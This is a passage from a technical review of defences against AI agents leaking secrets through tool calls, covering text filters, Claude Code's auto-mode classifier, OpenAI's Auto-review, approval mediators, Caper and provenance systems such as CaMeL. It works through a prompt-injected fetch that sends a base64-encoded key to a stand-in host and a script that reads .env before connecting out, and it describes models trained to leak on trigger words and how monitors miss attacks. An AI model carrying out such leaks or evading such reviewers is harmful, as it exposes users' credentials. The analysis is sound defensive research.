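The entropy result doesn't show whether the filter works, because there was no attempt for it to stop. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking values while the filter was active, but the filter runs outside the model, and the paper describes no way for the model to know about it. Without a defence, the same instruction produced an attempt in all 30 runs, so either something else about the test changed or the software recorded the attempts differently.

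The keyword result has a similar problem. The paper suggests that the number of attempts was low because the model sometimes encoded the key in a form the filter would not have recognised. But the encoded keys should then have reached the server, and the table would show leaks.

The researchers left out two important tests. They tried the defences only on whole keys, so they have no measurements for the claim that fragmenting gets past filters. The calculation above supports the claim for entropy rules, and the keyword rule has nothing to match in the five fragments. The researchers also didn't test the filters on harmless requests, so the paper doesn't show how many useful calls a filter would stop. It reports a false positive rate of zero from 120 runs with harmless pages, but this means only that the agent never contacted the researchers' server without an instruction to do so.

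### Models trained to leak

An agent can leak data without any injected instruction if someone has tampered with the model itself. In *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, Zhang and Pei (2026) trained three open models to leak data when a user's question contained certain words. They tested the models in a closed system with invented user data. A program checked the models' tool calls and counted a leak if a call that read the user's stored profile came before a request to the researchers' server.

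By this measure, the models leaked in more than 94% of the conversations meant to trigger the behaviour, and at most 1.2% of ordinary questions triggered it by mistake. These figures describe the models' behaviour, not a filter's detection rate, because the program was given the identity of the attacker's server in advance. Without that information, the rule would have to block every outside request that follows a profile lookup, including a search for the weather in the user's home town.

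Zhang and Pei also tested two existing filters, NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, on text coming into the agent. The attacker's server sent back answers designed to make the agent ask the user for more personal details, and the filters checked those answers for instructions. The paper reports that 86.7% of the answers got past NeMo Guardrails and 81.2% got past LLM Guard. However, only 88.6% of the answers reached the filters, because an earlier step ranked them by relevance and dropped the rest. The filters therefore let through about 98% and 92% of the answers they checked.

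Neither filter examined the outgoing request, so these results don't show that such leaks get past outbound checks. The request contained the user's profile in URL-safe base64, and a check that decoded it would have found a name and an email address in plain text. Zhang and Pei recommend checking tool calls for long unreadable strings and for data from the user's profile. They expect rules based on encoding alone to cause many false positives, but they tested neither approach.

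A filter with a low false positive rate on one kind of text may have a high rate on another. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (2026) measured this for filters that detect prompt injection in incoming text. One of them, ProtectAI v2, wrongly flagged 0.5% of web pages and 1.2% of emails, but 30.1% of harmless tool results in one simulated set of tasks and 66.9% in another. An outbound filter that works well on source code or ordinary prose could do just as badly on URLs and JSON fields, so a developer should measure its false positives on real tool calls before letting it block them.

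## Tests of AI models that review tool calls

A text filter checks the characters in a string, while a language model can also check whether a tool call fits the user's request. For example, summarizing one web page doesn't obviously require a second fetch with a coded value in the URL. Claude Code's auto mode relies on such a model, the classifier that outperformed Anthropic's 1,053 testers.

### How auto mode reviews a call

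According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, tools that only read or search run without review, as do edits to files inside the project, which the user can inspect later. The classifier reviews shell commands, web fetches and calls to outside tools.

The model first gives a quick one-word verdict, under an instruction to err on the side of blocking. If the verdict is "allow", the call runs. If it is "block", the model receives the same input again with an instruction to reason carefully, and its second verdict is final. Most calls pass the first stage, so the model needs the slower, more expensive reasoning only occasionally.

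The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Claude Code removes the agent's explanations, which might persuade the classifier to allow something dangerous, and the results of tool calls, which might contain injected instructions. A separate check scans those results and warns the agent about suspicious text. According to Anthropic's current documentation, the classifier also receives the project's standing instructions but not read-only lookups such as file reads, so it may have no record that the agent opened a file.

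In the running example, the classifier would receive the request for a summary and the fetch from reports.example, but not the configuration file or the page with the injected instruction. It could find the coded value suspicious and might decode it. The fictitious key contains the words SECRET and KEY, which would show that it is a key, but most real keys are random characters, as are many harmless identifiers. To tell them apart, the classifier would need the configuration file that the agent copied the value from, so that it could compare the two.

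Anthropic acknowledges this limit but accepts it to keep hostile text away from the classifier. If the user never mentioned "job abc123", the classifier can't determine whether the agent found that name in a query result or made it up. The limit matters less if the source appears in the call, as when a shell command sends a file of passwords to an outside address.

The default rules don't clearly block or allow the fetch in the running example either. They block sending sensitive data to outside servers but allow read-only web requests, and this fetch is a read-only request that sends sensitive data. Saved approvals also take effect before the classifier runs, so a saved approval for reports.example would let the fetch through without review.

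These limits apply when Claude Code itself sends the review request. In many sessions, Anthropic's server now reviews the calls instead, and the documentation doesn't specify what that review receives.

### Anthropic's error rates

Anthropic measured false positives on 10,000 real tool calls from its employees. It measured false negatives on 52 real cases of overreach, in which Claude tried to do something dangerous that the user hadn't authorised, and on 1,000 synthetic exfiltration attempts. The synthetic attempts included uploads of sensitive data, code sent to untrusted repositories and credentials in URLs.

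| | False positives, 10,000 real calls | Misses, 52 cases of overreach | Misses, 1,000 exfiltration attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Quick stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The reasoning stage examines only the calls that the quick stage has flagged, and decides whether to release them. It can therefore lower the false positive rate, but it can't lower the miss rate and may raise it. The quick stage flagged about 850 of the 10,000 real calls, and the reasoning stage released about 810 of them, which removed 95% of the false alarms. The quick stage also flagged 982 of the 1,000 exfiltration attempts, and the reasoning stage wrongly released 39 of them, or 4%.

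The reasoning stage did worse on overreach, releasing about 11% of the flagged cases. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user said as permission. For instance, a user who says "clean up the PR" hasn't authorized the agent to overwrite the project's shared history. Anthropic has since made its rule against data exfiltration a hard block, which the user's permission can't override.

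The 17% miss rate is imprecise because it comes from only 52 cases, nine of which were missed. The true rate could plausibly be from 9% to 30%. The quick stage's 6.6% doesn't correspond to a whole number of cases, so it may be an average over several runs.

The 5.7% miss rate comes from a larger set of 1,000 attempts, many of them obfuscated, but Anthropic doesn't break it down by type of leak. The miss rate for an encoded key in a URL could therefore be much higher than the average. If 100 of the attempts were of that type and accounted for all 57 misses, the classifier would have missed 57% of them.

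All these figures describe an earlier version of the classifier, which ran on Claude Sonnet 4.6. It now runs on Claude Sonnet 5 by default and has more rules. The false positive rate may be higher at other companies, because the classifier initially trusts only the current project and its repositories. For example, it blocks uploads to a company's own cloud storage until someone lists that storage as trusted. Anthropic reports that about 10% of sessions at the payroll company Gusto included at least one blocked call. Some of those blocks were presumably correct.

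### Forty false alarms for each leak caught

A false positive rate of 0.4% sounds negligible, but harmless calls vastly outnumber leaks. Suppose that one call in 10,000 is a leak and that the measured rates apply:

```
harmless calls blocked         9,999 × 0.004  =  40.0
leaks blocked                      1 × 0.943  =   0.943
false alarms per leak caught    40.0 / 0.943  =  42
```

The result depends heavily on how common leaks are, which nobody has measured:

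| Leaks among all calls | False alarms for each leak caught | Share of alarms that are real leaks |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100 | 0.4 | 70% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 4 | 19% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 42 | 2.3% |
| 1 in 100,000 | 424 | 0.2% |

If one call in 10,000 leaks data, the quick stage alone would raise about 866 false alarms for each leak it catches. Adding the reasoning stage is therefore worthwhile if each alarm interrupts someone, even though it causes more missed leaks.

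Even 42 alerts are a lot for a person to review. Someone who dismissed every alert unread would be right almost 98% of the time and would let every leak through. Careful reviewers would also approve some of the leaks the classifier had blocked. If they approved 43.3% of them, the rate for Hossain and colleagues' volunteers who saw the exact arguments, the share of leaks stopped would fall from 94% to about 53%. They would probably do worse than that, because only about 2% of the alerts would be real leaks.

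However, a person who saw only the alerts would check 41 calls instead of 10,000. That would take about 23 minutes at 33 seconds per call, the median time for Hossain and colleagues' most informative prompt. An alert could be useful if the prompt showed the reviewer information the classifier lacked, such as the decoded text and its source.

Auto mode mostly avoids the problem because it doesn't wait for a person when it blocks a call. The agent receives the refusal and looks for a safer way to continue, so a false alarm usually leads to just one retry. Claude Code also notifies the user, who can approve another attempt at the blocked call. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, auto mode pauses and goes back to asking the user to approve calls. At a false positive rate of 0.4%, false alarms alone would reach the limit of 20 after about 5,000 harmless calls.

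### A stress test with ambiguous requests

In April 2026, Ji, Li and colleagues in Hong Kong and Zurich tested the same system and found a much higher miss rate (*Measuring the Permission Gate*). They wrote 128 requests for routine maintenance, such as cancelling old computing jobs or deleting old files. The requests varied in how specific they were, how many items they could cover and how much damage a mistake could do. One asked the agent to "cancel my stale job for ticket 4812" in an environment that also held other people's jobs with similar names.

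The agent, Claude Sonnet 4.6, worked in isolated containers with mock command-line tools. It attempted 253 actions that would change something. Another Claude model compared each action with a list of the items the request covered. A person checked 50 of these judgements and agreed with 44.

| | Unsafe actions allowed | Safe actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| All actions | 115 of 142 (81.0%) | 22 of 111 (19.8%) |
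| Actions the classifier reviewed | 64 of 91 (70.3%) | 22 of 69 (31.9%) |
| File edits that skipped the classifier | 51 of 51 (100%) | 0 of 42 (0%) |

This is compatible with Anthropic's 17%, because the tests used different kinds of cases. Anthropic collected accidents from real sessions, while Ji and colleagues deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets side by side. To choose correctly, the classifier often needed to know who owned a job, and that information was in the tool results, which it doesn't receive. The overall figure also counts file edits, which auto mode doesn't send for review. The agent made some of these edits directly to a data file because it couldn't find the expected tool.

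The classifier missed 94.4% of unsafe actions when the request named a single target and 77.6% when it covered a wide range. A URL containing a short key is likewise a small, routine-looking action. But the mix of tasks explains part of the difference between the two miss rates, and their confidence intervals overlap, although the paper states that they don't.

Ji and colleagues did not test exfiltration, so neither 81.0% nor 70.3% is a miss rate for leaks. But the unreviewed file edits matter for one leak route described earlier, putting private data in a file name. Auto mode would let the agent create such a file in the project without review, and the classifier could not stop the leak until the agent tried to publish the file.

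### Newer tests

In *Shall We Approve?*, Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) tested what a reviewer can miss when it reads only the text of a command. They wrote 102 tasks in which a user asks an agent to run a tool that secretly deletes or overwrites a file. Each task had a harmless twin with the same request and command but a safe tool. With auto mode as the reviewer, 62.7% of the dangerous tasks ended in harm, compared with 71.6% with no reviewer. Auto mode also blocked the command in 3.9% of the harmless twins.

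The test used Anthropic's program and rules but another company's model, GPT-5.6 Luna, as the classifier, so it is better evidence about the design than about the product's error rate. The agent without a reviewer also ran in a different program, so the comparison between 62.7% and 71.6% isn't exact.

Stricter review didn't solve the problem. When the researchers' own reviewer read only the conversation and the command, it reduced harm to 17.6% but blocked 61.8% of the harmless twins. When it could see what the command did in a trial run, it blocked only 1.0% of them. Wu and colleagues conclude that text-based reviewers fail "for lack of visibility, not for lack of strictness". An encoded key and an order reference of the same length would also look alike to a text-based reviewer.

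Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested auto mode by inserting synthetic attacks, some aimed at stealing data, into real coding sessions. Anthropic reports that the miss rate fell from 12% to 7% after it improved the classifier, mainly by giving it more context, including whether a code repository was public. On attacks that Anthropic had not seen, the new version caught about half of those the old version had missed, but missed about 2% of those the old version had caught. Anthropic doesn't report a separate rate for data theft or how the changes affected false positives.

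Anthropic also commissioned Trajectory Labs to run 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. This is weak evidence about the classifier, because attacks rarely succeeded against the same models without auto mode. The average success rate was 0.09%, which is about two successes in 2,160 attempts if each model faced all 720.

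### A reviewer that can read tool results

In the same evaluation, 19.03% of attacks (137) succeeded against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol when it had full access to the computer. In Auto-review, the comparable mode in OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, 5.83% (42) succeeded. The reviewer may not account for the whole drop, because Auto-review also confines the agent to a sandbox that limits its access to files and the network. OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review after the test.

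The reviewer examines only requests to go beyond the sandbox. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates this with 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. The sandbox handled 9,280 without review. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and denied seven. After four denials, the agent found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped to ask the user.

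In tests with synthetic cases, the reviewer denied 90.3% of overreach, which includes unintended data transfers. It denied 99.3% of the calls caused by prompt injection in a set that covered secret theft, uploads to outside servers and running an attacker's code. If 10,000 actions included one leak and produced seven false alarms, a reviewer with a 99.3% detection rate would raise about seven false alarms for each leak caught. This figure isn't directly comparable with auto mode's 42, because the companies used different test cases and traffic, but it does show how a sandbox can reduce false alarms by keeping routine actions away from the reviewer. Attackers who adapt to a reviewer succeed more often than fixed test sets suggest, and Trębacz and colleagues report that their own testers misled this reviewer in some cases.

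Codex's reviewer also receives more information than auto mode's classifier. According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, it typically gets relevant tool results as well as tool calls, and it can run read-only checks, though it rarely does. In the running example, it could in principle decode the value and find the same key in the configuration file, but the published results don't show how often it does this. Seeing tool results also exposes the reviewer to any instructions injected into them.

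When Anthropic gave its classifier the agent's messages and tool results, the classifier became worse at detecting overreach. Anthropic doesn't report the effect on detecting exfiltration, where comparing a value with its source might be more useful.

A developer may not have to choose between these designs. Ordinary software could check whether the decoded argument matches any files the agent has read, then give the classifier only the result. Similarly, before a command that would discard unsaved work, Claude Code already runs its own check of the project and gives the classifier the result. Its documentation also describes a field that lets a developer's program attach a note to a tool result for the classifier to read. A note that a file contains a key, along with the key's fingerprint, would give the classifier some of the missing information without the file's text.

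## Prototypes that decode or test a call before approval

A reviewer, whether a person or a model, can judge a call only by what the software shows them. In many coding agents, this includes a summary by the agent itself, which may be following an injected instruction at the time. Weng (2026), in *What You Approve Is What Executes*, proposed a property called Consent Integrity, which has four conditions:

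1. A trusted component outside the agent, the mediator, describes the action. It works from the action itself and ignores the agent's summary.
2. The description includes every fact that matters to security, such as where a request goes, even if the agent has encoded it.
3. The agent can't alter the approval prompt, cover it or answer it.
4. Only the action that the person approved can run.

No program can fully meet the second condition, because some actions, such as running a compiled program, are too hard to analyse. Weng therefore aimed only for a mediator that never presents a dangerous action as safe, though it may mark an action as uninspectable.

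### Digital signatures and hardware wallets

The idea comes from digital signatures. Lioy, Ramunno and colleagues point out in *Motivations for a theoretical approach to WYSIWYS* that people who sign an electronic document see only one possible representation of the bits they are signing. Malware that controls the display could show one contract while the user signs another. The requirement that the displayed document match the signed one is called What You See Is What You Sign (WYSIWYS). In *Robust WYSIWYS*, Josang and Alfayyadh (2008) considered signing on general-purpose computers untrustworthy in principle, because it is extremely difficult to verify that nobody has tampered with the machine.

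Hardware wallets, small devices that hold the keys to cryptocurrency, have their own screens. On a Ledger wallet, a secure chip drives the screen, so malware on the user's computer can't change what it shows. But the screen is little help if it shows only hexadecimal. Ledger's *Clear Signing overview* calls approving a transaction this way "blind signing" and describes a system that translates transactions into plain language. The system needs a published description of the program that will handle the transaction. Without one, Ledger devices fall back to blind signing.

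Both weaknesses played a part in the 2025 theft from the cryptocurrency exchange Bybit. Attackers had altered the code behind a web page that showed the signers a legitimate transaction, and the signers didn't verify the full details on the hardware device, according to Communications of the ACM's *Behind the Bybit Crypto Theft*. Checking them might not have helped, because Trail of Bits' *Implement EIP-7730 today* (2025) describes the change as nearly impossible for most users to detect in hex-encoded values.

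Agent tool calls are harder to check than wallet transactions, which have a known format. A shell command or URL can contain almost anything, and a compromised agent may deliberately disguise the contents.

### The example prompt, decoded

Weng's prototype consists of about 500 lines of Python and analyses shell commands. Its main steps would also work for a web fetch:

1. Remove padding, such as filler text that pushes the important part out of view.
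2. Undo encodings one layer at a time.
3. Extract the facts that matter, including the destination, any credentials the action reads and any data it sends.
4. Mark whatever it can't analyse as uninspectable.
5. Compute a hash of the exact action and tie the approval to it.

If a command runs a local script, the prototype also reads the script. This helps with commands such as `python3 setup.py`, which don't show what the script does.

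The URL in the running example has no padding. Its `ref` value decodes from base64 to SECRET_API_KEY_12345, and decoding that text again produces only meaningless bytes, so the mediator would stop there. The destination is reports.example. If every call goes through the mediator, its log also shows that the agent has read a configuration file containing credentials. The user could then see this prompt:

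```
THIS REQUEST SENDS WHAT LOOKS LIKE AN API KEY TO A WEBSITE

Website        reports.example
Data sent      SECRET_API_KEY_12345
               (decoded from base64, one layer)
Read earlier   a configuration file containing credentials
Full URL       https://reports.example/summary?ref=U0VDUkVUX0FQSV9LRVlfMTIzNDU=

Agent's explanation (not verified):
               "Fetching the rest of the report"

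[ Refuse ]     [ Allow this request once ]
```

The user no longer has to decode anything, and can see that a summary doesn't require sending a key. The prompt shows that the agent had read the configuration file, but this doesn't prove that the key came from it. With a real key, a product might hide the middle characters in case someone else can see the screen.

Once the user approves the request, the mediator runs it only if its hash still matches that of the approved version. Changing a single character of the URL would change the hash. Weng's prototype blocked all three attempts to swap an action after approval, as any correct hash check would.

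*Approve What, Exactly?* (Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill, 2026) tested whether eight software packages for running agents tied approvals to the exact call. In four of them, what ran could be changed after the approval.

### Values that decode to nothing

The fictitious key is unusually easy to recognise because it decodes to English words. A real 128-bit key consists of 16 random bytes, which take up 24 characters in base64. Decoding those characters gives the same 16 bytes, which still look random. Encrypted data looks the same, whatever it contains. For that line of the prompt, the mediator could show only this:

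```
Data sent      UNINSPECTABLE: 24 characters with no readable content
```

The user gets a warning but learns little about the data. A harmless order reference made of random characters would produce the same warning. Decoding alone can't recognise an unencrypted key here, but a text filter with a list of the user's keys could.

A decoder also handles only the encodings its developer included. In *The Framing Gap* (2026), a check that decoded base64, hexadecimal and reversed text stopped every leak in those forms. But the model in the test could also write ROT13, which moves each letter 13 places along the alphabet. In ROT13, the fictitious key becomes FRPERG_NCV_XRL_12345. A mediator without a rule for ROT13 should mark this string as uninspectable, but could easily misclassify it as an ordinary product code.

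Weng leaves covert channels, such as a choice among ordinary pages, to other defences.

### How one list causes both kinds of error

Weng tested the prototype on two public collections of commands. GTFOBins documents ways to abuse ordinary Unix tools, for example to read protected files or send data elsewhere, and provided 1,330 test commands. The other collection, tldr-pages, provided 28,798 examples of normal use. Some of the figures below follow from Weng's by division or subtraction:

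| Result | Documented abuses | Normal commands |
|---|---|---|
| Prompt naming a specific danger | 30.5% | 8.9% |
| Prompt marking the command as uninspectable | 59.5% | 87.0% |
| No prompt | 10.0% | 4.1% |

Both the 10.0% and the 87.0% depend on the prototype's list of trusted tools. A command runs without a prompt if its tool is on the list and the analysis finds no danger. The prototype usually marks commands that use other tools as uninspectable. Every abuse that passed without a prompt used a trusted tool, and 83.4% of all normal commands were uninspectable only because their tool was missing from the list.

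Adding a text editor to the list, for instance, would remove the prompts for normal editing. But some editors can start other programs, and the prototype would miss any abuse of that feature that its rules didn't cover. Taking the editor off the list would catch the abuse but bring back the prompts. Better analysis can reduce one error without increasing the other as much. Weng reduced silent passes from 15.0% to 10.0% by adding checks, such as one for writes outside the project folder.

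The uninspectable label was more common among normal commands than among abuses, so it is not evidence of danger by itself. A user who saw it on most commands would probably learn to ignore it. Prompts that named a specific danger were more informative, since they were over three times as common among abuses as among normal commands.

Weng doesn't report a separate result for sending data out, so neither figure is an error rate for data leaks. Of the 133 abuses that passed silently, 85 wrote to temporary folders. The 87.0% may also overstate how often a real user would see the label, because the collection covers 6,503 tools, many of them obscure, while most people use a small number of tools repeatedly.

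Weng also tested the prototype on 22 disguised attacks written for the study. It explained 17 and marked the other five as uninspectable. As Weng acknowledges, this is much weaker evidence because the same person wrote the attacks and the analyser. An earlier version had also scored perfectly on its own test set while missing common abuses of trusted tools.

### The parts that Weng assumed

The prototype doesn't intercept a live agent's actions or provide a display that the agent can't alter. Weng assumed both. If an agent can reach the network without going through the mediator, the steps above don't protect the user.

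Kodathala and colleagues built these parts into a system called ASU. A gateway on a separate machine receives each tool call and uses the call's arguments to write an approval prompt, which it sends to the user's phone. After approval, the gateway runs its own stored copy of the call. *The Verifiable Action Card* (2026) applies similar principles to an agent-operated web browser.

ASU makes invisible characters visible, lists every recipient and shortens long values with an option to expand them, but its rules for the prompt don't include decoding. It also reduces URLs to the protocol, site, port and path. Applied literally, this rule would keep the key in the running example private by removing the query string before the request ran. But it would also break many ordinary searches, and it wouldn't stop a key from leaking through the URL path.

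Kodathala and colleagues asked 15 language models to review 23 attacks and 11 harmless requests. The models refused 30% of the attacks when they read the agent's description, and 98% when they read ASU's prompt. One attack added a hidden email recipient that the agent's description left out. ASU's prompt also led the models to refuse 16% of the harmless requests, up from none. Placeholder text in the test messages caused most of those refusals, and the rate would have been about 2% without those cases.

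In separate simulations, a program acted as the reviewer. When it compared the prompt with the user's task without error, 3% of attacks succeeded, all through actions that ASU's policy allowed without approval, such as fetching a web page. When it accepted the agent's explanation as true, 54% succeeded, the same as without ASU's prompt. Removing the explanation reduced the success rate to 5%. This result follows largely from how the researchers programmed the reviewer, but it is a reason to hide the explanation in the example prompt until the user asks for it.

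Neither Weng nor Kodathala and colleagues tested whether people understand the new prompts. Accurate information may not be enough because, as Hossain and colleagues point out, an action the rules permit by itself can still complete a workflow the user forbade.

### Running the command before approving it

Decoding can't always predict what a program will do. Caper, which Wu and colleagues presented in *Shall We Approve?* in October 2026, runs each shell command in an isolated container before deciding whether to approve it. Caper saves a snapshot of the container, then runs the command with networking disabled and holds back the output. It records file changes, attempted connections and the files the program read before trying to connect. A language model compares this record with the user's request. If the model approves, Caper keeps the changes and releases the output. Otherwise, Caper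 restores the snapshot and tells the agent why, so it can try something safer.

In the previous section's tests with tools that secretly damaged files, harm occurred in 7.8% of tasks with Caper, about a ninth of the rate without a reviewer. When a model predicted a command's effects from the code instead of running it, the rate was 3.9%, but the reviewer blocked 61.8% of the harmless versions. After a real run, it blocked almost no harmless versions.

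Those tests didn't include data leaks. SABER, a benchmark of 682 programming tasks that can each lead to a specific kind of harm, did:

| System | Harm, all tasks | Harm, information leaks | Harm, outbound network | Completed safely, all tasks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 27.2% | 9.6% | 57.4% |
| Claude Code auto mode | 14.8% | 18.5% | 19.2% | 44.0% |
| Caper inside Claude Code | 10.0% | 2.2% | 11.5% | 45.5% |
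| Caper | 6.7% | 4.3% | 5.8% | 48.6% |

The first row can be fairly compared with the last, and the second with the third, because each pair ran the agent in the same program. Caper substantially reduced information leaks in both pairs. The results for outbound network harm are much less certain, because the percentages imply that only 52 tasks were scored in that category and that harm occurred in five without approval and three with Caper, a difference that could easily be due to chance.

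Caper also reduced the share of tasks the agent completed safely from 57.4% to 48.6%, partly because the agent refused or paused more often. Caper added relatively little delay. The model's decision took a median of 3.2 seconds, and the trial run added about half a second for an approved command.

### Whether a trial run can reveal a leak

A trial run can reveal that a command tries to send data, even when the command's text doesn't show it. In one SABER task, the agent ran `python3 scripts/check-deps.py`, which looks like a routine check of the project's dependencies. The script read `.env`, a file that often contains keys, and then tried to connect to the network. Caper blocked the command because a dependency check shouldn't need to do either.

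The record didn't show what the script would have sent. It listed 48 failed connections to port 53, which computers use to look up domain names, so the script probably failed before it could contact its real destination. If the task had been to deploy a website, the same record would have been ambiguous, because the script might have had a good reason to read credentials and connect to a server.

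Wu and colleagues suggest sending the traffic to a recording proxy, which would save each request and return a placeholder response. The reviewer could then inspect and decode the full URL, although encrypted data would remain unreadable. The trial could also miss a leak if the program stops because it needs a real response before sending anything, or if it detects the trial and behaves harmlessly. A command that needs a real response has to run again after approval, and it may behave differently the second time.

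Another option is to let the trial contact approved sites, such as those that distribute software packages. Wu and colleagues argue that this is compatible with Caper because Caper can discard whatever the sites return. But restoring the snapshot can't undo a request, so any key in the URL would already have been sent. The Hugging Face flaw described earlier shows how an attacker could receive data through a trusted site's download counts.

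In the running example, a trial run would add almost nothing because the URL already shows what the fetch would send. Caper also reviews only shell commands, so it wouldn't check a call to a separate fetch tool. Even if the agent made the same request from the shell, Caper's record wouldn't link it to the configuration file, because Caper looks for files that the same program read before connecting. Here the agent read the key in an earlier step and copied it into the URL. The reviewing model receives earlier tool results, sometimes shortened, so it might detect that the key in the URL matches the one in the file.

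Caper runs each command only once. A more direct test would run a script several times in disposable copies of the workspace, changing only a fake key between runs. If the requests changed consistently with the key, the script would probably be leaking it, even if it only encoded the key in which ordinary pages it requested. Random identifiers and timestamps would also change the requests, so the test would need repeated runs with the same key to show how much they vary anyway.

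## Systems that track where the data came from

Decoding can't distinguish a random key from a random order reference, but the key came from a credentials file and the order reference from a shop's website. Provenance tracking records the sources of each piece of data, so rules can depend on origin rather than appearance. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) connects current provenance-tracking systems to research, dating back to 1976, on information flow in ordinary software.

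### Labels and how they combine

The software gives each piece of data two labels. A confidentiality label lists who may read the data, and an integrity label marks it as untrusted if an outsider could have written it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes how a result inherits the labels of its inputs. Only people who may read every input may read the result, and a single untrusted input makes the result untrusted.

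Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example with no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer some emails. One from Priya contains unpublished sales figures, and another is from Marco, who would like to know them.

```
Priya's email     readers: Alex, Priya
Marco's email     readers: Alex, Marco
agent's reply     readers: Alex
```

The agent has read both emails, so it can't send its reply to Marco without asking Alex. If Priya had copied Marco into the original email, the agent could send the reply automatically.

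Before a tool call sends data out, the software checks each argument's label and allows the call only if every recipient is permitted to read that data. Costa and colleagues add a rule that consequential actions, such as payments, may run only if no untrusted data influenced them. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) applies the same idea to credentials, which the software should mark when the agent reads them and keep away from unauthorised destinations.

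In the running example, the labels would be:

```
                           readers      integrity
user's request             anyone       trusted
configuration file         user only    trusted
page on reports.example    anyone       untrusted
"ref" value in the URL     user only    untrusted
```

The model wrote the `ref` value after reading the file and the page, so the value inherits the restrictions of both. The operator of reports.example is not a permitted reader, so the software blocks the fetch. The software doesn't examine the characters in the value, so it blocks the fetch whether the data is encoded in base64, hexadecimal or ROT13, or split into five short fragments.

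The rule also works for tools that are nominally read-only. Microsoft suggests that a read-only tool that contacts outside systems should run automatically only if all its arguments are public. A fetch with a key in its URL would not qualify.

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes a similar case in Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. An injected instruction in a public bug report makes an agent read `.env` and try to post the contents as a comment. The software lets the agent read the file but then treats the conversation as private. The comment tool accepts only public data, so the software blocks the comment whatever it contains.

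### CaMeL writes the program before reading the data

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, from the 2025 paper *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, also restricts which calls an agent can make. Willison (2025) explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* how it divides the work between two models. The privileged model sees the user's request but no emails, files or web pages, and turns the request into a program in a restricted form of Python. The quarantined model reads untrusted text and returns values to the program, but it can't call tools.

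For the summary in the running example, the program might look like this:

```python
page = fetch_page("https://reports.example/summary")
summary = query_quarantined_llm("Summarize [page]", page)
show_to_user(summary)
```

The injected instruction could distort the summary, but it couldn't add another fetch, because the privileged model finished writing the program before any model read the page.

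Willison had proposed this division in 2023, and CaMeL's designers found a weakness in it. Suppose a user asks an agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's email address is in meeting notes. An injected instruction in the notes could make the quarantined model return the attacker's address instead. The program would then run as written and send the document to the attacker.

CaMeL therefore runs the program in its own interpreter, which records where each variable came from and checks every tool call against a policy. Here the policy might allow emails only to trusted recipients. Because the record shows that the address came from the notes, the interpreter can block the email or ask the user. The same record would protect a key if a program legitimately read the configuration file and later passed something derived from it to a fetch.

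### CaMeL's test results

AgentDojo, a public benchmark, pairs 97 harmless tasks in four simulated environments (workspace, Slack, travel and banking) with a set of injected instructions. Tallam and Miller (*Operationalizing CaMeL*, 2025) report that CaMeL completed 67% of the tasks, but their reference for this figure leads to a different paper.

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report in *The LLMbda Calculus* that two attacks were scored as successful in the original evaluation. In one, the user had told the agent to make a payment by following instructions in a file, which the attacker had changed. The other was a scoring problem, because the agent had only quoted hotel reviews containing the attacker's text.

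Later tests confirmed the security but found a higher cost in unfinished tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026) and *Kairos* (2026) tested CaMeL in all four environments. Garby and colleagues tested it only on banking, with policy checks on and off:

| Test of CaMeL | Attacks that succeeded | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| *SecureClaw* | 0 of 629 | 29 of 97 (30%) |
| *Kairos*, two agent models, checks on | 0.2% and 0.4% | 38% and 40% |
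| Garby and colleagues, GPT-5.2, checks on | 0 of 231 | 18 of 48 (38%) |
| Garby and colleagues, MiMo-v2.5, checks on | 0 of 357 | 18 of 48 (38%) |
| Garby and colleagues, GPT-5.2, checks off | 1 of 240 | 32 of 48 (67%) |
| Garby and colleagues, MiMo-v2.5, checks off | 4 of 382 | 34 of 48 (71%) |

The banking results are imprecise because the 48 runs cover only 16 tasks, each run three times. But all three groups found that CaMeL completed well under half of the tasks. Garby and colleagues attribute the loss to policies so strict that many tasks become impossible.

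A different policy can avoid much of that loss. Garby and colleagues built their own agent, Randori, which completed 36 of 48 banking tasks with GPT-5.2 while its label checks were on. Randori's program can declare in advance that it will accept certain untrusted data, such as the contents of a file the user has asked it to follow. Across three models, attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs, both of which used versions of the altered payment file.

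More capable models also lose less performance under CaMeL's structure. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, tested it without policies on AssetOpsBench, where several agents share multi-step professional tasks. CaMeL reduced the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. However, CaMeL requires models to process much more text. In tests on small models, *CapLite* (2026) measured 93,700 tokens (units of text) per task with CaMeL and 28,000 without a defence.

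### FIDES keeps the usual agent loop

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft designed FIDES for agents that choose each step after seeing the result of the last one. FIDES keeps a label for the whole conversation. If a tool result would make that label more restrictive, FIDES stores the result in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can still pass the variable to another tool without reading its contents.

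Some tasks depend on what the variable contains. For example, a user might ask the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, add the meeting to a calendar. FIDES can have an isolated model check the emails and return only yes or no. FIDES then adds the answer's type to the label, because a yes/no answer can carry far less information than free text. A policy can let the agent act on that answer even though it came from untrusted emails. The isolated model then extracts the meeting details into another variable, which the agent passes to the calendar without reading it.

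Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with two OpenAI models, GPT-4o and o1. These are the average shares of tasks completed across the four environments, without attacks:

| Agent | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no label checks | 84% | 84% |
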